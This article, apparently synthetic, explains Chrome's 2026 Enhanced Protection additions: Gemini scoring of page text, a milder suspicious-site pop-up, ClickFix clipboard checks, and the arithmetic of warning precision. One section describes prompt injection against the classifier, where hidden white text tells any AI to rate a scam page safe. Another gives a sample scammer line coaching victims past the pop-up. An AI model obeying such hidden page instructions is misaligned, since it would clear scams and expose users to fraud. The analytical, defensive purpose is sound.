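# Chrome's Gemini scam detection and ClickFix warnings of October 2026

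## What Google announced and how Chrome already warned about dangerous sites

Google's web browser, Chrome, warns people before they open a page that Google considers dangerous. On 20 October 2026, Google described three additions to these warnings in a blog post, "Our latest defenses against evolving web scams", by Jasika Bawa, a Group Product Manager for Chrome. Help Net Security covered the post the same day in *Chrome flags malicious commands that scammers pass off as fixes* (2026), and Rijo (2026) described it in detail four days later in *Chrome adds suspicious-site warnings for 1 billion Enhanced Protection users*.

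When a page shows strong signs of a scam, Chrome now has Gemini check the page's text. Gemini is Google's large language model, an AI model that is trained on text and can describe or classify a page. This stronger model runs on Google's servers and takes over from Gemini Nano, a small version that ran on the user's device. Chrome also has a new, milder warning for sites that look like scams when Google is not certain that they are. It now also warns people when a web page gets them to copy a harmful command. In this trick, which security researchers call ClickFix, the page claims that something is broken, and the "fix" it offers is a command that installs malware once the victim pastes it into a system tool and runs it.

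All three additions are for people who have turned on Enhanced Protection, an opt-in mode of Safe Browsing, Google's service for judging whether sites, downloads and other content are dangerous. Chrome's default is Standard Protection, and KultureGeek's *Google Chrome renforce sa protection contre les arnaques avec Gemini* reports that Google has not confirmed any of the new warnings for Standard users. Users can turn on Enhanced Protection in Chrome's settings, under "Privacy and security" and then "Security". Chrome Security reported in its summary of the last quarter of 2025 that this choice now carries over between Android and desktop for people who sync their preferences. Google last counted Enhanced Protection users in 2025, when there were more than a billion.

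### How Safe Browsing checks an address

Google launched Safe Browsing in 2005 to protect people from phishing, in which fake pages collect passwords or card numbers. It later extended the service to malware, unwanted software and social engineering, which means tricking a person instead of breaking into a machine. Chrome uses the service, and so do others, including Google's advertising staff, who use it to keep ads from promoting dangerous pages.

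The service is built around lists of unsafe websites. Google's systems examine sites and add thousands of unsafe ones to the lists every day, according to *Real-time URL protection while preserving privacy*, prog.world's repost of a Google announcement. The announcement put the number of protected devices at more than 5 billion.

When someone clicks a link or types an address, Chrome computes a hash of the address, which is a fixed-length string produced by a formula. The same address always gives the same hash, and in practice no other address does. Chrome takes the first part of the hash, called the prefix, and looks for listed sites whose hashes begin the same way. Usually there are none, and the page opens. If there are any, Chrome compares the full hashes. If one matches, the address is on a list, and Chrome shows a full-page red warning instead of the page. The user can turn back or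 continue anyway.

Chrome used to make the first comparison on the device, against a downloaded copy of the lists that it refreshed every 30 to 60 minutes. Google considered this too slow because 60% of phishing sites existed for less than ten minutes, according to *Google Chrome gets a visual makeover*, a news story from the browser's fifteenth anniversary in 2023. Standard Protection now sends the prefix to a Google server at the moment of the visit. Comments in the source code of Chromium (2017), the open-source project from which Google builds Chrome, describe these real-time lookups as the replacement for lookups in the local database. Chrome encrypts each request and sends it to Google through a relay.

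The real-time check removes the delay in updating a phone's copy of the lists, but not the delay before Google finds a new dangerous page. Suppose that scammers put up a fake parcel-delivery page at 9:00, send the link to thousands of phones and take the page down at 9:09, and that Google's systems find it at 9:04. Under the old arrangement, a phone that refreshed its copy of the lists at 9:30 would have got the new entry after the page had gone. With a real-time lookup, everyone who taps the link from 9:04 onwards can get the red warning. A person who taps it at 9:02 gets no warning under either arrangement, because nobody has examined the page yet and it isn't on the list. The absence of a match means only that Google has no finding against the address, which is very little evidence that a two-minute-old site is safe.

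Some scam sites also use cloaking, which means they detect the automated programs (crawlers) that inspect the web and show them a harmless page, while human visitors get the scam. Such a site can stay up for days, pass an inspection and remain off the lists. PYMNTS's *Google Expands AI Tools to Combat Evolving Scam Tactics* gives this as a reason for checking pages inside the browser, where the software can examine the same page the visitor sees. Moving to a model on Google's servers should largely preserve this advantage, because the text Gemini reads there still comes from the visitor's browser.

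### What Enhanced Protection adds

Both modes use the lists. Enhanced Protection adds checks that can catch a page or file for which no entry exists.

| Check | Standard Protection | Enhanced Protection |
|---|---|---|
| Address against lists of known bad sites | Yes | Yes |
| Enhanced Protection's own models for imitations of trusted sites and for known attack patterns | No | Yes |
| Automatic deep scan of suspicious downloads | No | Yes |
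| Gemini analysis of page text | No | Yes |
| Milder warning for suspicious sites | No | Yes |
| Check of copied commands for ClickFix | No | Yes |

Google's *Defending 1 billion Chrome users with Enhanced Protection* illustrates the second row with a fake parcel page. The models detect that the page imitates a well-known delivery company but has an unrelated address. Unlike a list, this works on the first victim's first visit. The drawback is that Google receives more data about what its users browse and, since the latest additions, about some of what they copy. Gangwar (2026), in *Chrome can now share your clipboard data with Google servers*, described Chrome's scam protection as both better and more intrusive.

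Deep scans are rare. In 2025, Google put the number at more than 300,000 a month. Across more than a billion users, that is roughly one scan a month for every 3,300 people, so most will hardly ever encounter this part of Enhanced Protection.

The two modes are also less clearly separated in Chrome's code than a table suggests. Chromium has a switch to turn off certain on-device page-load scans for Standard users, which implies that Standard users had those scans when the developers wrote it. Chrome checks downloaded Android app files by default for everyone with Safe Browsing on. The two modes look up addresses differently, and the developers gave Chrome a way to repeat a sample of Enhanced users' lookups with the Standard method, to find sites that the Enhanced lookup clears but the Standard one would flag. They evidently thought this could sometimes happen.

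### From 2020 to the 2026 additions

Google introduced Enhanced Protection in 2020 and has been adding to it since. In 2021, Chrome 91 added deep scanning of downloads. Users had to approve the scan of each file until Google made scanning automatic in Chrome 125, in 2024.

In its notes on Chrome 134, from February 2025, Google told administrators that the browser would use a large language model on the device to help identify scam sites for Enhanced Protection users. Google announced this publicly in May 2025 in Bawa and Parakh's *How we're using AI to combat the latest scams*, which presented new AI defences across Chrome, Search and Android. Rijo dates the use of Gemini Nano to Chrome 137, released that month. Google aimed the model at tech support scams, in which a page poses as a computer company's help desk and reports an invented fault.

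Gemini Nano ran only on some devices, as KultureGeek notes. A model on Google's servers does not depend on the user's hardware. ETV Bharat's *Chrome Adds New Defences To Fight Online Scams* (2026) reports that Google is extending the Gemini checks to everyone who has Enhanced Protection on, and that they now also cover fake antivirus and browser-update pages. This may be the largest of the three changes for people with older or cheaper machines, who may have had no language-model check before.

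### When the new features reached users

According to Rijo, Google presents all three features in Bawa's post as additions made during 2026, rather than on the day of the post, and gives no Chrome version number, rollout schedule or list of platforms. menow.fr's *Chrome renforce ses alertes contre les faux antivirus* also describes the post as a summary of the year's changes and warns against assuming that every user received the same new protection on 21 October.

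The three additions were probably not yet close to general release at the end of March 2026. Google's *Chrome Enterprise and Education release notes* (2026), in the 31 March edition for Chrome 147, do not list them among current or planned browser changes. The omission is weak evidence, but the same edition does cover a smaller Safe Browsing feature (a menu item for reporting scam pages), and the Chrome 134 notes covered the on-device model three months before its public announcement. The warnings about unencrypted (HTTP) sites are a separate change, which Google had planned for Enhanced Protection users in Chrome 150 and for everyone in Chrome 154. Kovacs (2026) reported them in the same week as the scam defences, in *Google Hardens Chrome Against ClickFix Attacks, Insecure HTTP Connections*.

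Signs of the additions appear in Chromium's code from May 2026, when a Google engineer, Awad Osman, added a switch for "Suspicious Site Warnings", as Chrome Story's *Chromium Tests Flag to Warn Users on Suspicious Sites* (2026) reported. The switch was off by default and applied only to desktop systems (Windows, Mac, Linux and ChromeOS). By early August the code also had switches for querying Gemini on Google's servers, for replacing the on-device model with a server model on Android, and for running a check when a page copies something to the clipboard. These switches show that developers were building or testing the features, but not that anyone outside Google had them.

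There is better evidence that the Gemini checks were live by the day of the announcement. In a 20 October social media post reproduced by ETV Bharat, Chrome wrote that the browser "is now using Gemini" against scams such as fake antivirus pages.

The ClickFix check is the only feature with a reported version number. CNews' *Браузер Chrome будет читать текст из буфера обмена*, a Russian report that cites the technology site Neowin, gives Chrome 155 as the first version to include it. The release dates make this plausible. Google had planned to release a new version every two weeks from Chrome 153, in September 2026, and Releasebot's *Google Chrome Updates & Release Notes* (2026) reproduces a Google notice that Chrome 155 and 156 both reached the stable channel, the edition for ordinary users, in October. With two weeks between them, Chrome 155 would have reached users by about 17 October,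 a few days before Bawa's post. But the notice is about tools for web developers and doesn't mention scam protection, so the claim that Chrome 155 introduced the check still depends on Neowin.

Two people with the same version of Chrome and the same Enhanced Protection setting could have different checks running on the same day, because Google can turn parts of Chrome on and off remotely. Its developers call the system for doing this Finch, and comments in Chromium's code recommend using it to roll out new versions of the Android scam model. The milder site warning began as a desktop feature, and the code from August has a server model for Android, but Google has not published a list of which additions work on phones.

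## How Gemini judges whether a page is a scam

Chrome's language-model check now covers fake tech support, fake antivirus alerts and fake browser updates. All three scams start with an invented problem on the victim's computer, but the scammers want different things.

A tech support scammer wants the victim to contact a fake technician, who then sells an unnecessary repair or asks for remote access to the computer. *Using AI to stop tech support scams in Chrome* (Bawa, Lim and Lu, 2025) describes pages that imitate security alerts, fill the whole screen and disable the keyboard and mouse to create a sense of crisis. A fake antivirus page lists infections that don't exist and offers a program to remove them, and the victim either pays for something useless or installs malware. A fake update page claims that the browser is out of date and offers malware as the update. It may not need to alarm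 the victim, because people are used to updating their browsers.

Phishing pages usually copy a real login or payment page to steal passwords or card numbers, so software can look for a familiar design and a form at an unfamiliar address. A fake antivirus page may have no form and needn't closely resemble any real page. The best evidence that it is a scam is often its message to the visitor, which a language model can read.

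In 2025, Google planned to extend the check to package-tracking and unpaid-toll scams. Help Net Security and Infobae's *Cómo activar en Chrome la protección con Gemini contra estafas en internet* (2026) do not list either type for the 2026 version. Those scams often end in a request for card details, so Chrome's phishing checks may already catch some of them. Google also seems to have begun expanding the check beyond tech support scams before moving it to servers, since its *Go behind the browser with Chrome's new AI features* promoted Gemini Nano for use against "more sophisticated scams".

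### The 2025 design

Certain page behaviors triggered the 2025 check. Bawa and her colleagues give one example, the use of the keyboard lock function, which lets a full-screen page receive keys that normally control the browser or the operating system, such as Escape. Online games and remote-desktop sites have good reasons to use this function, but scammers use it to make a page hard to leave. Google has not published the full list of triggers.

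When a trigger fired, Chrome used Gemini Nano on the device to extract "security signals" from the contents of the page, such as the page's intent. Chrome then sent these signals to Safe Browsing, which combined them with its existing data about the site to reach a verdict. If the verdict was that the page was likely to be a scam, Chrome showed a warning.

Gemini Nano reduced a page's text to a few facts, which Safe Browsing's existing systems could use with their other evidence to classify the page. The 2025 check therefore needed a connection to Google, even though the model ran locally.

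The model scanned only pages that set off a trigger, so most pages would never have reached it. For those that did, the scan could happen when a user clicked on the page, as Duffy (2025) reported in *Google is using AI to identify scammy websites on Chrome*. According to Bawa and colleagues, Chrome used the model "sparingly", kept track of how much text it had to process, and limited its use of the computer's graphics processor. Chrome also ran the model in the background so that the browser would not freeze. This means the page can stay on the screen while the model is working, and a frightened visitor may act before the warning appears.

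Google said Standard Protection users would benefit indirectly, because it would add newly discovered scam sites to the lists. This helps only if the site is still up when the next person visits, so the benefit is probably small for pages that disappear after a few minutes.

### The 2026 design

The 2026 version has the same general structure but uses the server model instead of Gemini Nano. Infobae notes that this version does not replace the lists of dangerous sites. A first screening checks for what Google calls "high-confidence scam indicators", and Chrome sends the page's text to the server only if the screening finds them.

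Gemini produces three outputs from this text, which Google, quoted by ETV Bharat, describes as the "brand represented, the intent of the page, and a scam likelihood score". The brand is the company or product that the page appears to come from, and the intent is what the page is trying to get the visitor to do. Google has not explained the score's scale, so outsiders cannot tell whether a score of 0.9, for example, would mean that nine in ten such pages are scams.

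Safe Browsing then combines the three outputs with the reputation of the site's domain (the main part of its address, such as example.com) and other security signals. Google hasn't listed those other signals or published how much weight each input gets. A high score from Gemini may be enough to flag a new site with no history but not a bank's website, though this is a guess from the general description.

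Of the three outputs, the brand is probably the most useful when combined with other signals. A page that presents itself as Microsoft's at an address unconnected to Microsoft is much more suspicious than a page with only one of these features, because a brand name or an unfamiliar address alone is almost no evidence of whether a page is honest.

### A fake antivirus page under both designs

Suppose someone looking for a free football stream clicks a button that opens a new tab. The tab fills the screen with the logo of a well-known antivirus company and a list of five infections. A countdown gives the visitor three minutes to "renew protection" before the computer shuts down. The scammer registered the domain two days ago, and no blocklist includes it yet.

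Under the 2025 design, Chrome uses a language model to check a page only if the visitor's computer can run Gemini Nano and the page sets off a trigger. Suppose that the page locks the keyboard, which is one such trigger. Chrome passes the page's contents to Gemini Nano, which summarizes the page as an attempt to frighten the visitor into buying security software. Safe Browsing then uses this summary and the fact that the domain is new to decide whether to show a warning. But Google built the first version for tech support scams, so even a correct summary might not have led to a warning. A scammer can also avoid the language-model check by leaving out the keyboard lock, as long as the page sets off no other trigger.

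Under the 2026 design, an old laptop gets the same check as a new one. The screening must still select the fake antivirus page for a check, perhaps because of its full-screen takeover or its address. Chrome then sends the page's text to Google's server, where Gemini names the antivirus company as the brand, identifies the intent as selling software through a false infection alert, and gives a high score. Safe Browsing finds that the domain has no connection to the company and no history. A warning is much more likely now that fake antivirus pages are one of the system's stated targets.

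The same evidence should also keep Gemini from mistaking honest pages that use similar words for scams. This table compares the invented scam with two harmless pages, assuming all three have passed the screening.

| Page | Brand represented | Intent | Domain | Reasonable verdict |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Fake infection alert | Antivirus company | Sell software through a false alarm | Two days old, no link to the company | Scam |
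| The real company's renewal page | Antivirus company | Sell software | The company's own, many years old | Harmless |
| News article that reproduces the fake alert | News outlet | Warn readers | The outlet's own, many years old | Harmless |

A simple search for phrases such as "your computer is infected" could flag the scam page, the renewal page and the news article. The renewal page is the harder of the two harmless pages to classify because its text may be almost as pushy as the scammer's, so the domain is the main evidence that it is legitimate. A model that interprets the text should identify the alert in the news article as a quotation.

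### Which reasons for working on the device still hold

In 2025, Google's reasons for running the model on the user's device included cloaking and the short life of malicious sites. Duffy also reports Bawa's argument that a local model was faster and better for privacy. Cloaking and the short life of sites still matter after the move to servers, but the speed and privacy arguments are now weaker or no longer apply.

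Bawa and colleagues wrote that the average malicious site exists for less than ten minutes. Google's *Browse safely with real-time protection on Chrome* had used the same figure to justify checking lists in real time for Standard users. If "average" means the arithmetic mean, almost no malicious site can last long, because a single site that stays up for 24 hours adds ten minutes to the mean of a group of 144. The median is a more natural reading. At least half of the sites would then be gone within ten minutes, while others could last for days. This would also fit the older statement that 60% of phishing sites lasted less than ten minutes.

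Google can also measure only the sites it finds. The data may leave out sites that stay hidden from its crawlers for a month or disappear before anyone notices them. The figure counts sites rather than victims, so a scam page that stays up for a week and attracts 50,000 visitors counts the same as one that lasts five minutes and attracts ten.

Google expected real-time lookups to block 25% more phishing attempts, which suggests that faster lists solve only part of the problem. If most attacks came from sites that lived for less than ten minutes and Google found those sites promptly, the gain over the old downloaded lists should have been far larger. Either many attempts come from longer-lived sites, or Google often finds the short-lived ones too late. Checking a page during the visit helps with late detection whether the model runs on a server or on the laptop, because Chrome can send the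 text of a two-minute-old page to either.

The argument from cloaking also holds, since the text still comes from the visitor's browser. *PhishFarm* measured how cloaking affects browsers' blacklists, using harmless PayPal-branded phishing sites that the researchers had permission to build. They ran preliminary tests in mid-2017 and reported the results to Google Safe Browsing and other organisations, but a full test in mid-2018 still found several shortcomings in the industry's defences. Those tests predate Enhanced Protection, so they are limited evidence of how well Google's crawlers do today. But they show why a crawler's view of a site is a weak basis for deciding that it is safe.

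Google's description of the server check mentions only page text, so a scammer might evade it by putting the whole alert into an image, which would leave very little text to send. Google may have a way of dealing with this, such as reading the words in images, but it hasn't described one.

The speed argument is harder to judge because Google has published no timings for the server check or the 2025 design. The server check has to send a page's text over the network and wait for an answer, but the 2025 design also had to contact Safe Browsing before it could show a warning. A large model on Google's hardware may well process a page faster than a small one on a cheap laptop.

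Chrome's scam detection now protects privacy less than it did in 2025, when it sent Google only the language model's summary of a page. It now also sends the page's text, which can include things the visitor would rather keep private. Google says it doesn't keep this text, but that promise is a weaker protection than leaving the text on the device.

In return, Google got a stronger model and reached people whose devices, according to Punto Informatico's *Google Chrome*, could not run Gemini Nano. TrendAI's *The Browser Is Now an AI Runtime* says that Chrome's on-device model is 4.27 GB and that Chrome installs it on qualifying desktops without asking. Gangwar recalls that users who found the file, named weights.bin, on their computers thought it was malware.

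Scammers should also find it harder to test their pages against a server model. According to TrendAI, any website with an encrypted (HTTPS) connection can run Chrome's on-device model, with no consent prompt or limit on use. A scammer with a suitable computer could therefore have tested hundreds of versions of a page in private, although the tests would have lacked Safe Browsing's half of the system. With a server model, the scammer can still open a page in Chrome and see whether a warning appears, but each attempt that passes the screening also shows the page to Google.

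### Why ask Gemini about a page that already looks like a scam?

Google says Chrome sends text only when a site already shows high-confidence signs of a scam, which raises the question of why Chrome doesn't simply show a warning at that point.

A strong indicator is probably not enough to identify a scam. A page that takes over the screen and locks the keyboard may be a scam or a game. The screening can detect this behaviour with little computation, and Gemini can then read the page to determine which it is. Some screening is also necessary because of the volume. When Google introduced real-time lookups for Standard users, Safe Browsing was assessing more than 10 billion addresses and files a day and showing more than 3 million warnings, or about one for every 3,300 assessments. Reading every page with a large model would use nearly all of the computation on harmless pages and would send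 Google far more of what people read.

As an invented example of what the second step can add, suppose the screening picks out 1,000 pages, of which 700 are scams. If Chrome warned about all 1,000, its precision (the share of warnings that are correct) would be 70%, which is far too low for a full-page red warning. Now suppose Gemini helps Safe Browsing clear 270 of the 300 harmless pages but also leads it to wrongly clear 35 scams. Chrome then warns about 665 scams and 30 harmless pages, so its precision is about 96%.

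Gemini can't catch scams that the screening misses. If the screening had missed another 300, Chrome would have warned about 665 of 1,000 scams, giving the system a recall (the share of scams it warns about) of 66.5%. Even a perfect model could not have raised that above 70%. The screening is therefore at least as important as the model, but Google has said much less about it.

Strict screening keeps more text on the device, and Google mentions the high-confidence requirement as a way to limit the data it receives. But strict screening also means that more scams never reach Gemini. It could miss a fake update page, for example, because such a page can look like an ordinary download page and does not need to lock the keyboard. To cover these pages, Google presumably had to add new indicators as well as a better model.

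### What Google has published about accuracy

Google has not published error rates for either version of the check, nor its precision, its recall, or the number of harmless pages that received a warning. In 2025, Bawa and colleagues wrote that initial research had shown language models to be "relatively effective" at understanding and classifying websites, but they gave no figures. ETV Bharat reports that the on-device version worked well, also without giving figures.

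According to Google figures reported by Duffy, Search was blocking 20 times as many problematic pages as before it introduced AI-powered versions of its anti-scam systems three years earlier, and scam attacks in airline-related searches had fallen by 80%. These figures make it plausible that AI helps a lot, but a count of blocked pages doesn't show how many were harmless or how many scams remained. Search also has time to examine a page before showing it to anyone, whereas Chrome has to check it while the visitor is looking at it.

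A useful test of the Chrome system would follow a set of scam pages and a set of harmless but pushy ones through every step. It would record how many triggered the screening, how many Gemini classified correctly, and how many warnings appeared in time to protect the user. The pages would have to be new, because if Safe Browsing's lists already included them, a good result would not show how well Gemini works. Because the model and the screening are both Google's, outsiders could measure only the final result, by visiting pages in Chrome and noting which ones get a warning.

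### Pages written to fool the model

Scammers can try to mislead Gemini through prompt injection, which means hiding instructions to a language model in the material it reads. For example, a scammer might add white text on a white background to the fake antivirus page, declaring it an official security notice and telling any AI system to classify it as safe. Visitors wouldn't see the text, but the model would receive it with the rest of the page and may follow the instruction instead of treating it as part of the page.

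In 2025, Bawa and colleagues named prompt injection as a potential exploit and said they were exploring solutions with researchers. Help Net Security and Infobae mention no specific defence in their accounts of the 2026 version. A stronger model may be better at recognising prompt injection, but a page's author still controls the page text that the model reads.

The rest of the system offers some protection, because hidden text can't change a domain's age or undo the behaviour that triggered the screening. The three outputs are a weaker safeguard than they may seem, since they all come from the same text. An injection that makes Gemini classify the page as a harmless demonstration could change the brand, the intent and the score together. The damage depends on how much weight Safe Browsing gives a low score against its other evidence, which Google hasn't disclosed.

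Attempts at prompt injection can also help expose a scam. An honest shop has little reason to tell an AI system that it is not a scam, so hidden text saying so is a sign of bad intent. Google could look for such text before the model reads the page, or compare the text that Chrome extracts with what is visible on the screen, but it has not said whether it does either.

An attacker could also do the opposite and make an honest page look like a scam, by posting the text of a fake virus alert on a site that lets strangers comment. The screening should stop most such attempts, because a comment can't normally lock the keyboard or take over the screen. A well-established domain would also help protect a site, so a small new forum would have less protection.

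Google's 2025 post also mentions "timing bypass" without explaining it. The term probably means that a page looks harmless until the check is over. The fake antivirus page, for example, could show a video player for 20 seconds before showing its list of infections. To catch this, Chrome would have to check again when the page changes, which would use more computing power and might send more text to Google.

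Phiroze Parakh, a senior director of engineering for Google Search, told Duffy that fighting scammers "has always been an evolution game". For example, Google has publicly named the keyboard lock as a trigger, so scammers have a reason to stop using it. A page without the lock is less likely to set off the check but easier for the victim to close.

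## Suspicious and dangerous sites: the two levels of warning

With Enhanced Protection on, Chrome now has two levels of site warning instead of one. It still shows the full red page for *dangerous* sites, which Google defines as having a "high confidence verdict, high risk of user harm". It shows a milder warning for *suspicious* sites, which have a "lower confidence verdict, possible risk of user harm". Rijo quotes the post as saying that the milder warning appears when a page "exhibits deceptive patterns commonly associated with known malicious sites". This means Google can warn about a page because it resembles scams, without evidence that it has harmed anyone.

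Google defines the two warning levels as if its confidence and the potential harm rise together, which isn't always true. It might be 95% sure that one page sells a useless $5 cleaning program, and only 50% sure that another will take $5,000 from the visitor's bank account. The expected loss is under $5 for the first page and $2,500 for the second. Google has not explained which warning pages like these would get.

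According to Google's *Manage warnings about unsafe sites*, a visitor has to select "Details" and then "Visit this unsafe site" to continue past the red page.

The warning for suspicious sites is a pop-up. *Chrome の新機能と ClickFix* (Spiegel, 2026) quotes The Verge's description of the page as "visible but darkened underneath", with an option to "Mark as safe" if Chrome has made a mistake. The other option is to go back to safety. Spider's Web's *Chrome ostrzeże cię, zanim będzie za późno. Przeglądarka stała się mądrzejsza* (2026) reports that the pop-up appears in the middle of the screen on phones and just under the address bar on computers.

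Leaving the page visible helps people recognise a site they know. It may also help scammers, because their text stays on the screen next to Chrome's. Fake antivirus pages already tell frightened people what to click, and one could add the line "Your browser may show a notice. Choose 'Mark as safe' to continue the scan." The trick's success would depend on how readable the darkened text is. It would be harder with the red page, since the scammer would have to coach the victim beforehand or over the phone.

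### The download warnings of 2024

Google took the two levels from Chrome's warnings about downloaded files. According to 9to5Google's *Google on how Chrome's new downloads tray UI is better for security* (2024), a grey triangle marks suspicious files, which means lower confidence and an "unknown risk of user harm", and a red stop sign marks dangerous ones.

Google's best evidence that two levels work comes from its download warnings. In a July post, Google (2024) reported that people bypassed fewer warnings and heeded them more quickly, but it gave no figures. It had also replaced its short messages with more detailed ones, so the improvement may have come from those rather than from the split into two levels.

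A mild warning is also safer for files than for web pages, because a downloaded file usually does nothing until someone opens it, which leaves time to check it. For Enhanced Protection users, Chrome can send a suspicious file for a deep scan. Google found that files sent for scanning were over 50 times more likely to be malware than downloads in general. With a suspicious page, the visitor already has it open and any Gemini check took place before the verdict, so the visitor has to decide without a further scan.

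### Google's argument for a milder warning

Google justifies the new level in one sentence of its post. The tailored design, it says, lets it "safely expand our coverage to display a higher volume of protective warnings". Spelled out, the argument needs five premises:

1. A mild warning does less damage than a red page when the site is honest.
2. Google can therefore show it on weaker evidence.
3. Some scams that used to get no warning, because the evidence was too weak for a red page, will now get one.
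4. Enough people who see the mild warning will leave.
5. The extra warnings will not make people careless about the red page.

The step from lower damage to weaker evidence is a matter of simple decision theory. Let *p* be the probability that a page is a scam, *L* the average loss to a visitor who stays on a scam page, *h* the share of visitors who leave when they see the warning, and *C* the average cost of the warning per visitor to an honest page. A warning does more good than harm when

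*p* × *h* × *L* > (1 − *p*) × *C*, or equivalently *p* > *C* ÷ (*C* + *h* × *L*).

In an invented example, a scam costs the visitor $100 on average. The red page makes 80% of people leave and costs $20 per visitor to an honest site, so Google should show it when the probability of a scam is above 20%. If a mild warning makes 40% leave and costs $5, the threshold falls to about 11%. But if the mild warning makes only 20% leave, the threshold is 20% again, so showing it at lower probabilities than the red page isn't justified.

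Much of the harm a warning does to an honest site comes from visitors leaving. If half as many people heed the milder warning, on scam and honest pages alike, both the harm and the protection fall by about half, so the threshold for showing it hardly changes. Showing the milder warning on weaker evidence is justified only if it annoys people less when they stay or helps them tell the pages apart, so that they leave scams more often than honest shops. Being able to see the page could help with this, though people who can reliably recognise a scam by looking at it don't need the warning.

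*Your Reputation Precedes You* (Almuhimedi, Felt and colleagues, 2014) found that Chrome users consistently heeded malware warnings about sites they had not visited before, but were less predictable about sites they knew. Most victims of a short-lived scam page have never seen it before, so they should tend to heed a warning about it. The same habit should reduce the harm a mistaken warning does to a shop with regular customers, but it won't help a new shop.

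### How many of the warnings would be correct

Scams are so rare among page visits that even a very accurate system can produce mostly false alarms. If *b* is the share of page visits that lead to scams, *r* the recall and *f* the share of harmless visits that get a warning, then

precision = (*r* × *b*) ÷ (*r* × *b* + *f* × (1 − *b*)).

As an invented example, suppose people load 50 billion pages a day and 1 load in 100,000 is a scam, which makes 500,000 scam loads. If Chrome catches 90% of them, it shows 450,000 correct warnings. If it also warns on 1 in 100,000 harmless loads, it shows about 500,000 false warnings, and only 47% of its warnings are correct. For 90% of its warnings to be correct, it would have to warn on only about 1 in a million harmless loads.

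No classifier that only reads text is likely to be that good by itself. But a first screening, like the one Chrome uses before it sends text to Gemini, makes the task much easier. Suppose the screening passes 1 page load in 1,000, including 95% of the scams. The classifier then checks 50 million loads, of which 475,000 are scams. If it recognises 90% of those scams and wrongly flags 1 in 1,000 of the harmless loads, Chrome shows 427,500 correct warnings and about 49,500 false ones.

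| Invented system | Correct warnings a day | False warnings a day | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|
| No screening, flags 1 in 100,000 harmless pages | 450,000 | 500,000 | 47% |
| No screening, flags 1 in 1,000,000 harmless pages | 450,000 | 50,000 | 90% |
| No screening, flags 1 in 1,000 harmless pages | 450,000 | 50,000,000 | 0.9% |
| With screening, flags 1 in 1,000 harmless pages it sees | 427,500 | 49,500 | 90% |

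The screening lowers recall from 90% to 85.5%. The result in the last row also assumes that the classifier is no more likely to make a mistake on pages that pass the screening than on ordinary pages. This is optimistic because the harmless pages that pass are the ones that look most like scams. If the classifier wrongly flags 1 in 100 of them, Chrome shows about 495,000 false warnings and precision falls to 46%.

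The best argument for having two levels comes from the same kind of arithmetic. Suppose Google's evidence is strong enough for a red page on 300,000 of the 500,000 scam loads, with 15,000 false alarms, which is a precision of about 95%. Lowering the threshold would catch another 120,000 scam loads but add 120,000 false alarms. If all these warnings were red, the red page's precision would fall to about 76%. With a separate pop-up for the additional pages, the red page stays at 95% and only the pop-up is wrong half the time. If half the people who see the pop-up on a scam page leave, it protects 60,000 visits a day and interrupts 120,000 harmless ones. Interrupting two harmless visits for each one protected seems reasonable when the loss could be someone's savings, provided that most honest sites get the visitor back.

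### Do people heed browser warnings?

The classic field study, Akhawe and Felt's *Alice in Warningland* (2013), used data that Chrome and Firefox reported during May and June of that year, covering 25,405,944 warnings that people saw in ordinary browsing. People continued past about a tenth of Firefox's malware and phishing warnings and a quarter of Chrome's. They ignored SSL warnings, which appear when the browser cannot verify a site's encrypted connection, much more often. Firefox users continued past a third of these, and Chrome users past 70.2%.

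Chrome users ignored about a quarter of malware warnings but 70.2% of SSL warnings, and this gap is the most relevant result for the new level. SSL warnings often appeared on honest sites whose owners had made a technical mistake. The researchers quoted in WeLiveSecurity (2013) took the 70.2% to mean that either people were ignoring valid warnings, or the browser was annoying them with invalid ones and "possibly causing warning fatigue". The designs of the two warnings also differed, so false alarms may not explain the whole gap. If people treat the new pop-up as they treated Chrome's malware warning in 2013, about three in four will leave a suspicious site, compared with only three in ten if they treat it like the old SSL warning.

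Later evidence suggests that people respond fairly well to Chrome's malware warnings but less well to other kinds. Almuhimedi and colleagues reported that a fifth of people continued past malware warnings. In February 2016, Chrome began to warn about sites that contained deceptive material from elsewhere, such as embedded content. Two months later, the Chrome engineer Engedy (2016) wrote in *Intent to implement* that "many users" went on to the pages anyway, and he proposed that Chrome also block some of the embedded material. This is an uncomfortable precedent for Google, which in 2016 also extended a strong warning to a new class of deceptive pages and found that the warning was not enough.

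A warning's design can greatly affect whether people heed it. When Google redesigned Chrome's SSL warning for version 37 so that its appearance steered people towards the safe choice, the share who heeded it rose from 37% to 62%. The suspicious site warning is less visually forceful than the red page, so fewer people might heed it.

The pop-up still interrupts the user, which is important. *Adapting Security Warnings to Counter Online Disinformation*, a 2020 study that borrowed methods from browser security, found that people routinely ignored notices beside search results but noticed warnings that blocked their way. _Oh, sh*t! I actually opened the document!_ (2024) cites similar evidence on phishing, where a full-screen browser warning kept more people from fake sites than a banner in their email program did. Chrome's pop-up covers less than a full screen, but the darkened page makes it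 hard to miss, so it should do better than a banner.

These studies are older than the new warning, and Google has published no click-through rate for it. *An Experience Sampling Study of User Reactions to Browser Warnings* (Malkin, Egelman and colleagues, 2018) is the nearest thing to a recent field test of browser warnings. It surveyed more than 6,000 Chrome and Firefox users about why they had just heeded or ignored a real warning. Their reasons varied with the situation, and no single failure stood out. This favours a warning that gives people some context, as Google says its new one does.

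### Would more warnings teach people to ignore them?

Psychologists use the term habituation for the loss of response to a repeated signal. According to research reviewed in *Revisiting the Design Agenda for Privacy Notices and Security Warnings* (2023), including brain-imaging experiments, people's response to a security warning drops from the second time they see it. The habit of ignoring one warning can also spread to similar ones, although attention recovers after a break. Akhawe and Felt concluded from their own study that designers should limit how many warnings people see, as reported in CRN's *Google Chrome Users May Suffer From Attack Warning Fatigue*.

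The habit of dismissing warnings spreads to similar ones, which is a good reason to make the pop-up look different from the red page. Someone who dismisses five mistaken pop-ups may stop reading pop-ups, but the red page will still look unfamiliar. If Google had also used the red page for its less certain verdicts, each false alarm would have weakened the most important warning.

The breaks between warnings are probably long too. At 3 million warnings a day across 5 billion devices, Safe Browsing shows about one warning per device every four and a half years. Even at ten times that rate, a device would get one only every five or six months. These are averages, and people who often visit illegal streaming sites must see far more warnings than people who mostly read the news. But for the typical user, Safe Browsing warnings alone are too rare to cause much habituation.

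The greater risk comes from other online interruptions, including cookie notices and other browser warnings. For example, Chrome asks permission before a user's first visit to any public site without encryption (Google, 2025). People who learn to dismiss that warning on old hobby sites might also dismiss the new pop-up, especially if the two look alike. *I'm trying not to get hacked* (2026) notes that most quantitative studies still find people dismissing security and privacy notices more often than is desirable. Some of the researchers it cites blame habituation, and others blame misunderstandings of the warnings.

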